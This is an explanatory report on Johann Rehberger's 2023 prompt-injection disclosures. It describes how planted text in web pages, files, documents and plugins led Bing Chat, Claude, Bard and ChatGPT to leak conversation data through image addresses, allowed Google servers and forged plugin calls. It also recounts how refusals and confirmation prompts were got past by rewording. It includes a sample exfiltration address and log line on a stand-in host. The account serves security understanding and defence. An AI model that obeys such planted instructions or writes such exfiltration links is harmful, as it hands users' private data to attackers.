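# Johann Rehberger's 2023 disclosures of data theft from chatbots by prompt injection

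## Rehberger, the attack in outline and the Ekoparty talk

In 2023 the security researcher Johann Rehberger showed that a stranger could steal private data from AI chatbot users by planting text where the chatbot would read it, such as in a web page, a file or a shared document. His demonstrations worked against Microsoft's Bing Chat, OpenAI's ChatGPT, Anthropic's Claude and Google's Bard. In most cases the chatbot put the data in the address of an image, and the chat window sent the data out when it automatically loaded the image. In other cases the data left through plugins, the add-ons that let ChatGPT use outside services such as a mailbox. Rehberger reported the flaws to the companies, described them on his blog and presented them at conferences, including Ekoparty in Buenos Aires in November 2023.

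Rehberger worked in conventional computer security before he turned to chatbots. He specialises in red teaming, which means attacking an organisation's systems on its behalf to find weaknesses before outsiders do. According to the biography in *Indirect Prompt Injections in the Wild*, the agenda entry for his Ekoparty talk, he set up a red team in Microsoft's Azure cloud business, ran it for years, and then built another at Uber. By the time of the talk he was Red Team Director at the games company Electronic Arts. The Chaos Computer Club's *Speaker Profile* shows that he still held that post when he spoke at a German hackers' congress in 2025. His blog, Embrace The Red, dates from December 2018, and he writes it under the handle wunderwuzzi.

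### How planted text becomes an instruction

A language model has no memory of its own, so the application around it stores the conversation and sends all of it again with every new question. The application adds the developer's instructions and any pages or files it has just fetched. The model answers from this combined text, which is called the context window. Rehberger explained this at the 37th Chaos Communication Congress (37C3) in Hamburg in December 2023, in a talk that volunteers of the Chaos Computer Club (2024) transcribed.

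The model receives the bundle as one continuous run of tokens (words and fragments of words) and predicts what should come next. A developer can label part of it as material only to be summarised, but the label is also just text, and nothing forces the model to ignore instructions in the material that follows. In Rehberger's simplest demonstration, an application asked ChatGPT to summarise a text that told it to skip the summary and print ten emoji, and ChatGPT printed the emoji. OpenAI had advised developers to enclose such material in triple quotation marks or rows of hash signs. Rehberger (2023) reproduced this advice in *Prompt Injections in the Wild*, his slides for the HITCON conference in Taiwan that August, and remarked that it does not work.

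Attacks of this kind have several names, and it matters who the attacker is. In a jailbreak, the user persuades the model to ignore its safety rules, for instance by inventing a character who has none. In a direct prompt injection, the user types something that overrides the instructions of the developer who built the application. Rehberger tried this on a restaurant ordering bot from an online course. He told the bot that a Diet Coke was on sale for nothing, and it wrote an order with a price of zero. He grouped jailbreaks with direct injection because the user is the attacker in both.

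In indirect prompt injection, a third party hides instructions in material that the chatbot reads, and the model follows them as if the user had given them. This makes the user the victim, who may only have asked for a summary of a web page.

The name and the first systematic account come from *Not what you've signed up for*, a February 2023 paper by Greshake, Endres and colleagues. They argued that an application that fetches outside text blurs the line between data and instructions, so processing a retrieved page comes close to running a stranger's program. They tested this on Bing Chat and on applications they had built themselves. Microsoft's Edge browser let Bing Chat read the page open beside it, and they found that text on the page could steer the model even when the user could not see the text. They listed possible harms including data theft, fraud, disinformation and self-spreading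 messages. Rehberger had been calling the same thing "AI injection" because, as he told the Hamburg audience, he did not yet know the literature. He credited Greshake and recommended the paper.

### One secret, step by step

An invented example shows how a planted instruction can lead to data theft. Early in a conversation, Ana asks a chatbot to draft a note giving her new tenant the burglar alarm code, 4417. The code is now in the chatbot's context window.

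A little later she asks the chatbot to summarise a page of reviews of removal firms. One reviewer has added instructions, in white text on a white background, for any AI that reads the page. The AI is to end its answer with a picture loaded from the reviewer's server, and to put any codes or passwords from the conversation at the end of the picture's address. The application fetches the page and places all its text, including the white text, in the context window with the alarm code.

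The model writes a perfectly good summary. Then it adds an image link. Chatbots commonly format their answers in markdown, a simple notation in which a few punctuation marks stand for bold type, a list or a picture, and in this notation a picture is just a caption and an address. The address that the model writes is this:

`collector.example/dot.png?note=alarm+code+4417`

Everything after the question mark is extra information for the server. Web shops pass along search terms the same way. The chat window converts the markdown into an ordinary web image, so Ana's browser requests the file from the reviewer's server, which logs the request.

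`14:02:51  GET /dot.png?note=alarm+code+4417`

The theft is complete at that moment, before the server returns any image. The server may return a single transparent pixel, in which case Ana sees only the summary, or it may return nothing. The attack is zero-click, meaning the victim doesn't have to click or approve anything when the data leaves. The reviewer's passage also stays in the context window, so the model can keep following it in later answers.

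This report uses the name markdown image leak for the method; Rehberger calls the flaw "image markdown injection".

The theft requires three things together: private data in the context window, text from an untrusted source in the same window, and a way to send data out. The programmer Simon Willison wrote in *GitHub Copilot Chat*, about a later case involving a coding assistant, that a chat interface has this vulnerability if it sees both private and untrusted data and displays markdown images. Removing any one of the three stops the leak, but some are easier to give up than others. People want a chatbot to know their private information and read the web, but few would miss images from unknown servers. GitHub fixed the flaw by blocking those images.

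### Who found the image leak

Roman Samoilenko, a software engineer, discovered the leak in ChatGPT at the end of March 2023, and Rehberger found it independently a few days later, in early April. Rehberger gives this order of events in *ChatGPT Plugins* (2023), and SecurityWeek's *Malicious GPT Can Phish Credentials, Exfiltrate Them to External Server* also credits both men with independent discoveries.

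*New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* describes Samoilenko's version of the attack, which starts on a website. When a visitor copies text from the site, a script secretly adds instructions to the end of it. The visitor pastes the text into ChatGPT, and the model adds an invisible one-pixel image to its answer, with data from the chat in the image's address. The instructions could also ask for such an image in every later answer, so that the attacker kept receiving the victim's questions.

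Rehberger acknowledged that the trick sometimes failed because ChatGPT's answers vary from one attempt to the next. He found it easy to extract the user's earlier questions or a piece of code, but very difficult to extract passwords or access keys. When ChatGPT was slow, a user might see the strange address appear letter by letter. He still thought OpenAI should stop ChatGPT from displaying markdown images at all. Willison's *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* (2023) brought the finding to a wider readership on 14 April.

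Samoilenko's attack required the victim to paste the poisoned text into the chatbot. Rehberger's attacks did not, because Bing Chat read the page the user had open and ChatGPT's new plugins fetched pages on request. An attacker could leave instructions in a comment on a web page for the chatbot to read.

### The talk in Buenos Aires

Rehberger's Ekoparty talk was titled "Indirect Prompt Injections in the Wild – Real World exploits and mitigations". The conference, a long-established gathering of Latin American hackers, ran from 1 to 3 November 2023 at the Buenos Aires convention centre, The Standard CIO (2023) reported. Class Central's *Indirect Prompt Injections in the Wild* lists the recording at 49 minutes. In his abstract, Rehberger said he would briefly introduce language models, go through exploits against ChatGPT, Bard, Bing Chat and Claude with a close look at the planted instructions,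 and describe the fixes Microsoft and Anthropic had made after his reports.

The details of the Ekoparty talk's argument come from two related talks, given before and after it. The sources are the slides from HITCON in August and the slides and transcript from Hamburg in December. Those two talks have a nearly identical structure, and the Ekoparty abstract fits it.

In both, Rehberger named three ways for data to leave a chatbot: links, images and plugins. The victim usually has to click a link, but programs such as Slack, Discord and Teams fetch it without a click, as soon as it appears, to show a preview. Images need no click either, as in Ana's case. With plugins, text that one plugin fetches can make the chatbot call another, which then sends the data out.

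A listener in Hamburg asked why an attacker would use images when many chatbots can open a web address. Rehberger answered that OpenAI had begun to ask users for permission before some of those visits, and that an image bypassed that request. Another listener asked whether a victim could notice the attack. Rehberger said it depended on the chat window, because some showed the address briefly while the model wrote it and others displayed the whole answer at once.

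Rehberger was pessimistic about defences. "There is no discrete deterministic solution", he wrote on his last technical slide in August, and he added that there might never be one. A deterministic defence is guaranteed by its design to work every time. Rehberger, who had once worked on Microsoft's SQL Server database, contrasted prompt injection with SQL injection, in which an attacker types database commands into a field meant for a name or a search term. The two attacks look similar, but a programmer can rule out SQL injection completely by building the query correctly, and nobody knew how to do the same for a language model. Filters, or a second model that checks the first, make a successful attack less likely but can't rule it out.

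That argument concerns the injection, and a firm defence against the leak is still possible. In the December slides, *NEW IMPORTANT INSTRUCTIONS*, Rehberger (2023) recommended a content security policy (CSP), a rule sent with a web page that specifies the addresses from which the browser may load images and other content. The browser enforces the rule whatever the model writes, so the protection depends on the list of permitted addresses, not on the model's judgement. Rehberger also advised treating everything a model writes as untrustworthy and having a person approve any serious action, such as sending an email.

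Rehberger's opinion on injection itself has held up. In April 2026, Adam Gavish of Google's AI security team wrote in *Google Workspace's continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* that indirect prompt injection is not a problem one solves and moves on from.

The companies' responses to the image leak changed over the autumn. Rehberger kept a list in his slides, with three products in August and seven by November:

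| Product | August 2023 | November 2023 |
|---|---|---|
| Bing Chat | fixed | fixed |
| Anthropic Claude | mitigated | fixed |
| ChatGPT | won't fix | won't fix |
| Google Bard | not listed | fixed |
| Azure AI (Microsoft's cloud service) | not listed | fixed |
| Vertex AI (Google's cloud service) | not listed | fixed |
| Discord | not listed | fixed |

The entries are his own summaries, and "fixed" means that the company had closed the leak he reported, even if the chatbot still obeyed planted text.

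### What "in the wild" meant

Rehberger used "in the wild" to mean that the flaws were in products the public was already using, rather than in laboratory models. Security people often use the phrase for attacks that criminals are using. In Embrace The Red's *ChatGPT Plugin Exploit Explained*, he used it for an exploitable flaw he had found in a live plugin, and he described most earlier demonstrations, including his own, as amusing and harmless. Willison (2023), in *Indirect Prompt Injection via YouTube Transcripts*, used the phrase the same way for instructions that somebody had deliberately added to the end of a video's transcript.

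Criminal use came later, and by 2026 observers had found many attempts but little proof of damage. In April 2026 Google published a search of Common Crawl, an archive that collects two to three billion public web pages a month. Its researchers searched for typical injection phrases, had the Gemini model sort the results and checked the remainder by hand. They found pranks, self-promotion and notices meant to keep AI systems away. Attempts at data theft were few and crude, but malicious injections increased by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026. The archive omits most social media and doesn't include private email or shared documents, where some of the most damaging instructions would be.

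Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, was more alarmed. In March 2026 it reported that attackers were using the method, and it counted 22 techniques for building and hiding the instructions. Its main example was a page selling "military glasses" at a fake discount, which contained 24 separate attempts to make an AI advertising checker approve it. But Unit 42 graded its cases by what the attacker wanted, and it knew of no confirmed success against a deployed advertising checker.

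Other security companies found attackers with clearer financial motives. Forcepoint identified ten sets of planted instructions aimed at committing fraud, destroying data and stealing access keys, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Uncover 10 In-the-Wild Prompt Injection Payloads Targeting AI Agents*. Zscaler documented two campaigns, one of them a payment scam disguised as software documentation, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents*. In both campaigns, the attackers first raised their sites' search rankings so that AI agents would be more likely to find them.

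## Leaks through images in Bing Chat, Claude and Bard

Rehberger tested the markdown image leak on Bing Chat, Claude and Bard between April and September 2023, and each company closed it in a different way. Microsoft restricted the servers from which Bing Chat could load images. Anthropic made Claude's users click before an image appeared. Bard already had a restriction like Microsoft's, but Rehberger got data past it through one of Google's own services.

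### Bing Chat

According to Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, an attacker could leave instructions for Bing Chat in a comment or an advertisement on an open web page. For his demonstration, Rehberger made a page with instructions at the top and a secret further down.

In the instructions, Rehberger told Bing Chat to announce that the injection had worked, wait for two turns of conversation, and then write an image link to his server. The link's address would contain a summary of the page and the conversation, about 200 characters long, along with any passwords or secrets on the page. Bing Chat was to encode all this in base64, which turns text into an unreadable string of letters, digits and a few symbols. At first Rehberger had the model build the link piece by piece, but he later found that it could fill in the missing part of an otherwise complete address.

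The secret arrived at his server with the rest of the encoded text. Rehberger added the delay to show how much control the page's text had over Bing Chat. A real attacker would leave out the announcement, so the victim would see two ordinary answers before the leak and have little reason to connect it with the page. The danger is greatest on pages that show private information beside other people's writing, such as a webmail inbox or a company forum.

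Rehberger reported the flaw to Microsoft on 8 April 2023, and Microsoft told him on 15 June that it had fixed it. He repeated his tests, and the attack no longer worked. In a 2026 post, Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, he dated the fix to May 2023. The June date is safer because he recorded it at the time, though Microsoft may have made the change some weeks before telling him. According to his account in Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON*, Microsoft was the first company to acknowledge and address the leak.

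Microsoft did not give him the full details, but he could see that Bing Chat now came with a content security policy. The policy travels in the headers, which are lines of technical information that accompany a page, and it has a separate list of servers for each type of content. In simplified form, Bing Chat's rule for images was this:

`Content-Security-Policy: img-src th.bing.com www.bing.com edgeservices.bing.com r.bing.com`

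`img-src` means "image source", and the four names after it are Microsoft servers. Bing Chat still had to load some images, for instance when a user asked it to create a picture. Before requesting any image, the browser checks whether the server's name is on the list. `collector.example` is not on it, so with this rule in place, Ana's browser would not have sent the request.

A rule of this kind has two limits. The browser checks only which server an address belongs to, not the data in the rest of the address, and a rule for images covers only images. In late 2025 Rehberger found that Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant for office work, could display small web pages inside a chat. The image rule blocked his server, but the rule for fonts was looser, so the browser requested a font from his server with the text of a private email in the address. Microsoft finished fixing this on 5 March 2026.

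Rehberger also noticed that Copilot's policy changed with the site hosting it, and that many versions allowed far too many servers. Some entries appeared to contain employees' usernames. He concluded that Microsoft could not rely on a CSP as a security boundary in Copilot, and suggested that the company also check whole addresses, as Google and OpenAI had begun to do.

### Claude

With Claude, the planted text was in a file that the user uploaded. Rehberger's test file was a short biography of Albert Einstein, with instructions in the middle of a paragraph for Claude to write an image link containing a 20-word summary of the user's earlier messages. Someone skimming the file could easily miss them. If a user had discussed a private matter with Claude and then asked about the file in the same conversation, part of that discussion would have been sent to the attacker.

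According to Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*, Rehberger reported the leak on 12 July 2023. Anthropic confirmed it on 18 July and closed the report on 26 July, two weeks after receiving it, whereas Microsoft had taken nearly ten weeks. As far as Rehberger could tell, Claude's chat window no longer loaded markdown images automatically. It displayed a "Show Image" button, and the browser contacted the image's server only if the user clicked it.

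Email programs have long used the same precaution. Gmail sometimes withholds the pictures in a message until the reader clicks "Show Images", as Second Thoughts' *Anatomy of a Hack* points out. A sender can give every recipient a different image address and learn from the requests who has opened the message. A chatbot can leak more this way, because the image address can contain the user's own words.

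The button stops the zero-click version of the attack. But Claude could still follow the planted instructions and write a link containing the data, so a single click would complete the theft. The user also has little basis for deciding whether to click, because an attacker who can dictate an image link can also dictate the sentence above it, and could have Claude introduce the picture as a chart that belongs to the summary.

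Rehberger accepted that the fix prevented automatic theft, but he called it imperfect and hoped for a better one in the long term. He did not give his reasons, but the obvious weakness is that the fix depends on the user's judgement. Anthropic later found that users of Claude Code, its programming tool, approved roughly 93% of the permission requests they saw. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* adds that users paid less attention as the requests mounted up. Those requests mostly concerned commands and file changes, so the figure doesn't measure how often people would click "Show Image", but it suggests that a button is a weak defence when people see it often.

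A company can avoid the problem by not displaying images at all. Google did this in Vertex AI's Generative AI Studio, a tool for developers. Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI* calls this probably the best possible fix for a product that doesn't need pictures. Microsoft made a smaller fix to its Azure AI Playground in September 2023, inserting a space into the image notation so that the chat window no longer recognised it, according to Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Fixes Data Exfiltration Vulnerability in Azure AI Playground*.

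### Bard

By September 2023, Google's Bard had Extensions that let it search YouTube, look up flights and hotels, and read the user's Gmail, Drive and Docs. Rehberger started with YouTube videos he had prepared for earlier tests, and Bard followed the instructions in them. Documents and emails worried him more, because an attacker can deliver them without the victim's consent. Anyone can share a Google Doc with a stranger, and the instructions in it take effect when the stranger's chatbot reads it.

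Rehberger credited Kai Greshake and Joseph Thacker with helping him develop the attack. Greshake's paper had given indirect prompt injection its name. Thacker, a security researcher known as rez0, also took part in a Google event for finding flaws in its language models (Carta, 2024, *We Hacked Google A.I. for $50,000*).

The first attempt to leak a conversation from Bard failed. Bard wrote an image link containing the conversation, but its content security policy (CSP) did not allow Rehberger's server, so the browser refused to load the image. According to Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard*, the policy did allow `*.google.com` and `*.googleusercontent.com`, where the asterisk stands for any name. Rehberger therefore needed a Google address at which he could receive data.

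He found one in Google Apps Script, a service for writing small programs that work with documents and spreadsheets, much like macros in Microsoft Office. Anybody with a Google account can write such a program and give it a web address on `script.google.com`. The attack then ran as follows:

1. Rehberger wrote a script that copied whatever came at the end of its web address into a Google Doc of his own. He named it the Bard Logger and changed a setting so that it ran for visitors who had not signed in.
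2. He wrote a second Google Doc for the victim. It told Bard to put the first 20 words of the conversation into an image address that led to the script.
3. The victim, who had already been chatting with Bard, asked it about this document. Bard wrote the image link.
4. The browser compared `script.google.com` with the policy, found that it matched `*.google.com`, and sent the request. The victim's words appeared in Rehberger's document.

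The attack was harder to carry out on Bard than on the other chatbots. Rehberger needed ten attempts, and had to include several examples of a correctly completed address before Bard put the words in the right place. He also presented the instructions as a requirement from a legal department. His demonstration extracted only twenty words of the conversation, but Second Thoughts observes that a real attacker could ask for a summary of the most sensitive parts.

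Rehberger reported the flaw to Google on 19 September 2023. On 19 October, he asked about its progress because he wanted to show the attack at Ekoparty. Google replied that he could go ahead because it had fixed the flaw, but didn't say how. He saw that the CSP had not changed and Bard still displayed images, so he inferred that Google had started to filter out addresses with data in them.

Willison (2023), in *Hacking Google Bard*, wondered how well the unexplained fix would resist variations of the attack. In June 2025 Google wrote that Gemini, as Bard is now called, recognises image addresses on outside servers and doesn't display the images. This fits Rehberger's guess about filtering, but it describes the product nearly two years later, so it can't confirm what Google changed in October 2023.

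### When an attacker can use an allowed server

Bard's policy kept the browser from contacting any server outside Google. But Google's servers also ran programs and stored documents for the public, so an outsider could collect data there. An allow-list of servers prevents a leak only if no outsider can receive data at any of them. Few large companies' domains meet that condition, because many of their services exist to accept material from customers.

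The email program Superhuman had almost the same flaw two years later. *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails*, published by the security company PromptArmor in January 2026, describes an attack that began with a message in the victim's inbox. The victim did not have to open it. When they asked Superhuman's assistant to summarise their recent mail, the assistant read the message along with the rest and followed its instructions.

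Superhuman's CSP blocked images from unknown servers but allowed `docs.google.com`, which also hosts Google Forms. The owner of a form can create a web address that contains an answer and submits it when opened. The assistant put the contents of the victim's emails into such an address and presented it as an image. When the victim's browser tried to load the image, it submitted the emails to the attacker's form. PromptArmor obtained the full text of several messages in one response and parts of more than 40 in another test.

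PromptArmor reported this late on Friday, 5 December 2025. Superhuman switched off the vulnerable features the following Monday and released a first fix on Tuesday and more over the next five weeks. In April 2026 PromptArmor also used a Google Form to collect emails from OpenAI's Codex, a flaw OpenAI has since fixed. PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* doesn't mention an allow-list, so the Codex case shows only that a Google Form is a convenient way to receive stolen data.

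A shorter list of allowed servers reduces the risk without removing it. Microsoft's 2023 policy for Bing Chat named four servers instead of a whole domain, and one of them was `www.bing.com`. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (June 2026) described an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot that used the same server. The browser sent the stolen data to Bing, as Copilot's policy allowed, and a Bing service passed it on to the attacker. The victim had to click a prepared link to start the attack, and Microsoft has fixed the flaw.

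An allowed domain can also get a new owner. Salesforce's policy still listed one of the company's old domains after the registration had expired, so researchers registered it and received data about sales contacts. Willison reported this and Salesforce's correction of the list in September 2025, in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*.

PromptArmor's *What domains should I add to my allowlist?* (2026) suggests questions to ask before allowing a domain. Could a customer get their own address there? Could an attacker have data submitted to a place they control, as with a Google Form? Does the service accept data from anyone who supplies an access key, including an attacker's key? Rehberger had shown in October 2025 that Anthropic's own servers had this last problem.

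This attack relied on programs rather than images. Claude had gained the ability to run programs in a sandbox, an isolated computing environment, from which they could reach a short list of approved servers. Most were approved so that Claude could download software, but the list also included `api.anthropic.com`, which customers' programs use to access Anthropic's services. One of these services, the Files API, stores files in the account whose access key comes with the request.

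In the attack described in Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate*, the victim asks Claude to analyse a document containing planted instructions and the attacker's access key. Claude saves private data, such as the text of the victim's last conversation, to a file and uses the key to upload it to the attacker's account. A single upload could carry up to 30 megabytes, far more than an image address can hold. The attack worked on Rehberger's first try, but Claude then refused repeatedly, partly because it treated the key as suspicious, until he disguised the request better.

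Rehberger reported this on 25 October 2025 through HackerOne, a service that handles such reports for companies. Within an hour he received a reply that it was out of scope because it concerned the safety of the model. He disagreed, writing that "Safety protects you from accidents. Security protects you from adversaries." On 30 October, after he had published the attack, Anthropic told him that such flaws were in scope and that it had wrongly closed the report because of an error in its process. SecurityWeek's *Claude AI APIs Can Be Abused for Data Exfiltration* also covered the reversal.

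Anthropic had warned users in *Create and edit files with Claude* that planted instructions could make Claude send data to outsiders, and recommended that they watch Claude work and stop it if it used data unexpectedly. Rehberger objected that people might assume the default setting, which allowed only the approved servers, was safe.

The correction in October did not close the leak. In January 2026, two days after Anthropic released a preview of Claude Cowork, its assistant for everyday office work, PromptArmor used the same method to steal a file of loan details from a test user's folder. Nobody had to approve the upload, according to PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files*.

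Anthropic later fixed the flaw in Cowork by adding a program that inspects requests to its own servers and passes only those carrying the current session's access token. The attacker's key no longer works, even though the server is still on the allow-list. Anthropic now regards an allow-list entry as a "capability grant", meaning it opens every function available at that address, including ones the product never needed. Rehberger had recommended much the same fix in October, when he said the sandbox should let Claude communicate only with the signed-in user's account.

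## ChatGPT plugins that acted on an attacker's instructions

In March 2023 OpenAI began letting outside companies connect their services to ChatGPT through plugins. The first partners included Expedia for travel, Instacart for groceries and Zapier, which automates tasks across other companies' programs. Rehberger found that a web page could make ChatGPT use such services for an attacker, with the user's permissions. OpenAI's launch announcement, *ChatGPT Plugins*, had already reported that testers found ways for plugins without safeguards to carry out prompt injection and send fraudulent emails.

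### How a plugin gained access to an account

A plugin ran on its developer's server, and the model had access only to a written description of it. *LLM Platform Security* (Iqbal, Kohno and Roesner, 2023) describes how ChatGPT used plugins. The developer supplied a description for the model and a list of the commands the plugin accepted. When a user switched the plugin on, ChatGPT added this material to the context window. The model then decided, from the wording of a question, whether to call the plugin and what data to send. OpenAI's servers made the request, and the plugin's answer was added to the context window.

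A user could enable up to three plugins in a chat, according to MIT Sloan. The plugins shared one conversation, so text from one could change how ChatGPT behaved when it used another plugin or none at all. Iqbal and colleagues found that the description of AMZPRO, a plugin for Amazon sellers, included an instruction to reply in English. With AMZPRO enabled, ChatGPT answered only in English for the rest of the session, even if the user never used the plugin.

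Plugins that needed access to a user's account, for example to read their mail, commonly used OAuth, a standard way to give one program access to an account held with another. According to OpenAI's instructions, which the Korean-language blogger 솔웅 (2023) copied out in *Chat GPT Plugin*, the user logs in on the plugin company's website while installing the plugin. The website then gives ChatGPT an access token, a code that stands in for the login. ChatGPT encrypts and stores the token, and attaches it to later requests to that plugin.

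The token identifies the user's account but doesn't show whether the user wanted a particular request. Rehberger's attacks exploited that gap, so they worked even when a developer had set up OAuth correctly. The security company Salt Labs separately found mistakes in the login process, including a guessable value where OAuth calls for a random one. An attacker might have used these mistakes to install a malicious plugin on someone's account. The companies fixed them, and Salt Labs saw no evidence that anyone had exploited them, according to TechTarget's *Researchers warn devs of vulnerabilities in ChatGPT plugins*.

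### The confused deputy

A confused deputy is a program that someone tricks into misusing its legitimate powers. The best-known example on the web is cross-site request forgery, which Embrace The Red illustrates with a home router. When the router's owner visits a web page, the page makes their browser send the router a command to change its firewall settings. The router accepts the command because it comes from the owner's browser, even though the owner never asked for the change.

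With plugins, ChatGPT could become a confused deputy too. Text fetched by one plugin could make ChatGPT call another, and the second plugin would receive a properly authorised request. In his post *ChatGPT Plugins*, Rehberger suggested calling this cross-plugin request forgery.

An attacker could gain more from a forged plugin request than from a forged web request. Browsers normally prevent one website from reading another's replies, so a forged web request can change a setting but rarely returns any data. ChatGPT, however, places the plugin's reply in the context window, and planted instructions can make the model pass it on. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Removes the "Chat with Code" Plugin From Store* points out that read-only commands are therefore also at risk.

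The image leak could expose only what was already in the context window. Ana's alarm code leaked because she had typed it into the chat. If she had connected her mailbox through a plugin, an attacker could have made ChatGPT search her mail for the code, or perhaps send messages in her name. A content security policy would not have prevented this, because OpenAI's servers, not the user's browser, send the requests to plugins.

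### From a flight search to a stolen email

Rehberger first saw one plugin trigger another when he had ChatGPT read a web page containing planted instructions. ChatGPT then used the Expedia plugin to search for flights without asking him.

Tom's Hardware's *ChatGPT Plugins Open Security Holes From PDFs, Websites and More* describes a repeat of the experiment. The reporter copied an article, added a request for flights from Seattle to Hawaii at the end, and asked ChatGPT to summarise it. WebPilot, a plugin for reading web pages, fetched the article. ChatGPT summarised it correctly, but then wrote that the reporter had mentioned wanting a flight to Hawaii, and used Expedia to recommend three flights. Booking one would still have taken a click, and Tom's Hardware cautioned that planted instructions might work only half the time or less.

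For a more serious demonstration, Rehberger looked for a plugin that could act as the user. He chose Zapier's, which could read a person's email, Google Drive and Slack messages. On 19 May 2023 Willison (2023), in *Let ChatGPT visit a website and have your email stolen*, called the result the first working attack of its kind that he had seen steal private data. It ran as follows:

1. The victim had WebPilot and Zapier switched on and asked ChatGPT to read a web page. WebPilot fetched the page, including Rehberger's instructions.
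2. ChatGPT called Zapier, which accepted the victim's authorisation and returned the latest email.
3. ChatGPT summarised the email in 20 words and added the summary to the end of an address on Rehberger's server.
4. ChatGPT had WebPilot open that address, and the request delivered the summary.

This attack used no image, and the victim didn't approve anything after asking about the page. ChatGPT sometimes stopped to ask for permission, so Rehberger wrote in the instructions that it didn't need any. He also made sure the attack worked from inside an ordinary web page, so an attacker wouldn't need to own the site.

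OpenAI had tried to make its own browsing plugin safer by letting it fetch pages but not submit forms. It conceded in the launch announcement that this reduced the risk but did not eliminate it. The last step of Rehberger's attack shows one reason, which is that a page's address can carry stolen data just as an image's can.

### Chat with Code and the plugin survey

The Chat with Code plugin let ChatGPT work in a user's account on GitHub, where programmers store and share code in repositories that can be private or public. Embrace The Red's *Plugin Vulnerabilities* describes a demonstration in which a malicious page made ChatGPT call the plugin and switch all the user's private repositories to public. Anyone, including the attacker, could then read the code on GitHub. Rehberger also published a milder version for people to try, which created a new repository and left a note in each private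 one asking why this was possible.

To see how many other plugins might have such powers, Rehberger downloaded the store's records, which listed 445 approved plugins. Of these, 51 used OAuth, which he took as a sign that a plugin probably acted for the user and might have access to personal data or computer systems. Over several weeks he tried a few and found others vulnerable to request forgery. Some would have let an attacker read personal data, steal secrets or run programs on remote machines.

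He didn't report how many he tried or how many resisted, so the survey gives no rate of vulnerability. The count of 51 could also miss some powerful plugins, such as ChatSSHPlug, which Iqbal and colleagues found asked users for the password or private key to their server. They recommended OAuth as a safer way to give a plugin that kind of access.

### Storing the whole conversation

Long texts are hard to fit into an image address, which limited the image leak. In September 2023 Rehberger got around this by combining the leak with plugins that create documents, diagrams or videos, as Embrace The Red's *Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT* explains.

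Such a plugin could save an entire conversation to a file, but it showed the link only in the user's chat, so an attacker wouldn't know where to find the file. Rehberger's planted instructions therefore told ChatGPT to record the conversation with any suitable plugin that the user had enabled, and then put the resulting link in an image address. When the chat window loaded the image, Rehberger received the link and could open the file. The link didn't grow with the conversation, so the length of the image address no longer limited how much he could take.

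In Rehberger's tests, Doc Maker produced a document, Show Me produced a diagram, and HeyGen produced a video with the conversation in its subtitles. A QR code plugin also worked, but its link contained the full text of the conversation, so the old limit still applied. ChatGPT had asked for further confirmation when he described the task as making a backup, but it complied when he used a more neutral word.

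A diagram plugin became dangerous when combined with ChatGPT's automatic loading of images, which OpenAI had already declined to change. A reviewer who examined the plugin by itself would probably have seen little danger in it. Rehberger sent OpenAI a draft of his findings on 23 September and received only an automated reply.

### Who had to fix it

Zapier responded promptly to the email attack by requiring the user's confirmation. Rehberger stressed that Zapier had to verify that the confirmation came from the user. If clicking a link in the chat had been enough to confirm, an attacker could have told ChatGPT to open it.

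OpenAI required plugins in its store to get the user's confirmation before taking an action, and named Zapier as the example to follow. It also required OAuth for any plugin that took actions in the world. A member of OpenAI's developer forum listed these among the store's rules in reply to Dariel, who had asked in *This plugin's service doesn't align with ChatGPT's accepted use cases* why OpenAI had rejected a video plugin.

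OpenAI also acknowledged the underlying problem on 13 June in *Function calling and other API updates* (2023), which mentioned a proof of concept in which text from a tool made a model do things the user had not intended. It advised developers to use only trusted tools and to ask for confirmation before sending an email, posting online or making a purchase. This advice and the store rule both concerned actions, which a developer could easily take to mean only operations that change something, but an attacker can steal an email through a plugin that only reads the mailbox.

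OpenAI enforced the store's confirmation rule unevenly. Chat with Code was in the store although it didn't ask for confirmation, and Rehberger wrote that he had contacted OpenAI about such problems at least four times, with little or no response. An accident appears to have finally led to the plugin's removal. A Reddit user reported that ChatGPT had unexpectedly created an entry in a GitHub project's list of bugs and tasks. The story reached the front page of Hacker News, a forum popular with programmers, and a few hours later OpenAI removed the plugin for breaking the rule. Rehberger noted on Embrace The Red that other plugins remained vulnerable.

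Iqbal and colleagues also reported their findings to OpenAI, which thanked them but said the issues posed no security risk to the platform. The researchers disagreed. At least one plugin company told them that only OpenAI could fix its problem, and that it had reported the problem to OpenAI but OpenAI had not fixed it.

Most of the work therefore fell to individual developers. Rehberger wrote to many of them privately, but some never answered, and some of their listed contact pages no longer existed. The store was also growing quickly. Iqbal and colleagues collected 268 plugins on 6 June and counted 799 on 1 August.

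Rehberger therefore wanted a control in ChatGPT itself, which would protect users of every plugin. He argued that one plugin should not be able to call another by default, and that users should see which plugin ChatGPT was about to call and what data it would send. He also recommended Willison's idea of dividing the work between two models, so that the model with access to tools is never given untrusted text and a second model without tools processes that text instead.

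Such separation keeps plugins from working together as freely. A shared conversation makes it easy to book a flight with one plugin and a hotel with another. Iqbal and colleagues thought a platform could keep much of this convenience by isolating each plugin and setting rules for what information could pass between them.

### After the 2023 plugins

Plugins never became very popular. A blog post, later withdrawn, quoted OpenAI's chief executive, Sam Altman, as saying that they had not yet shown product-market fit, meaning enough demand from users. Willison agreed in *ChatGPT Plugins Don't Have PMF*, writing that no outside company's plugin had become part of his routine. OpenAI stopped new plugin conversations on 19 March 2024 and allowed existing ones to continue until 9 April, according to *Plugin Store and New Chats With Plugins*. Custom GPTs, versions of ChatGPT that people set up for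 particular tasks, replaced plugins. They could also connect to outside services, and Salt Labs considered them more secure than plugins but still imperfect.

The weakness also affected ChatGPT's built-in tools. In 2024 Rehberger showed that a web page could make ChatGPT create a picture based on details it had stored about the user (Embrace The Red, *Automatic Tool Invocation when Browsing with ChatGPT*). A page could also trigger the memory tool, which stores those details.

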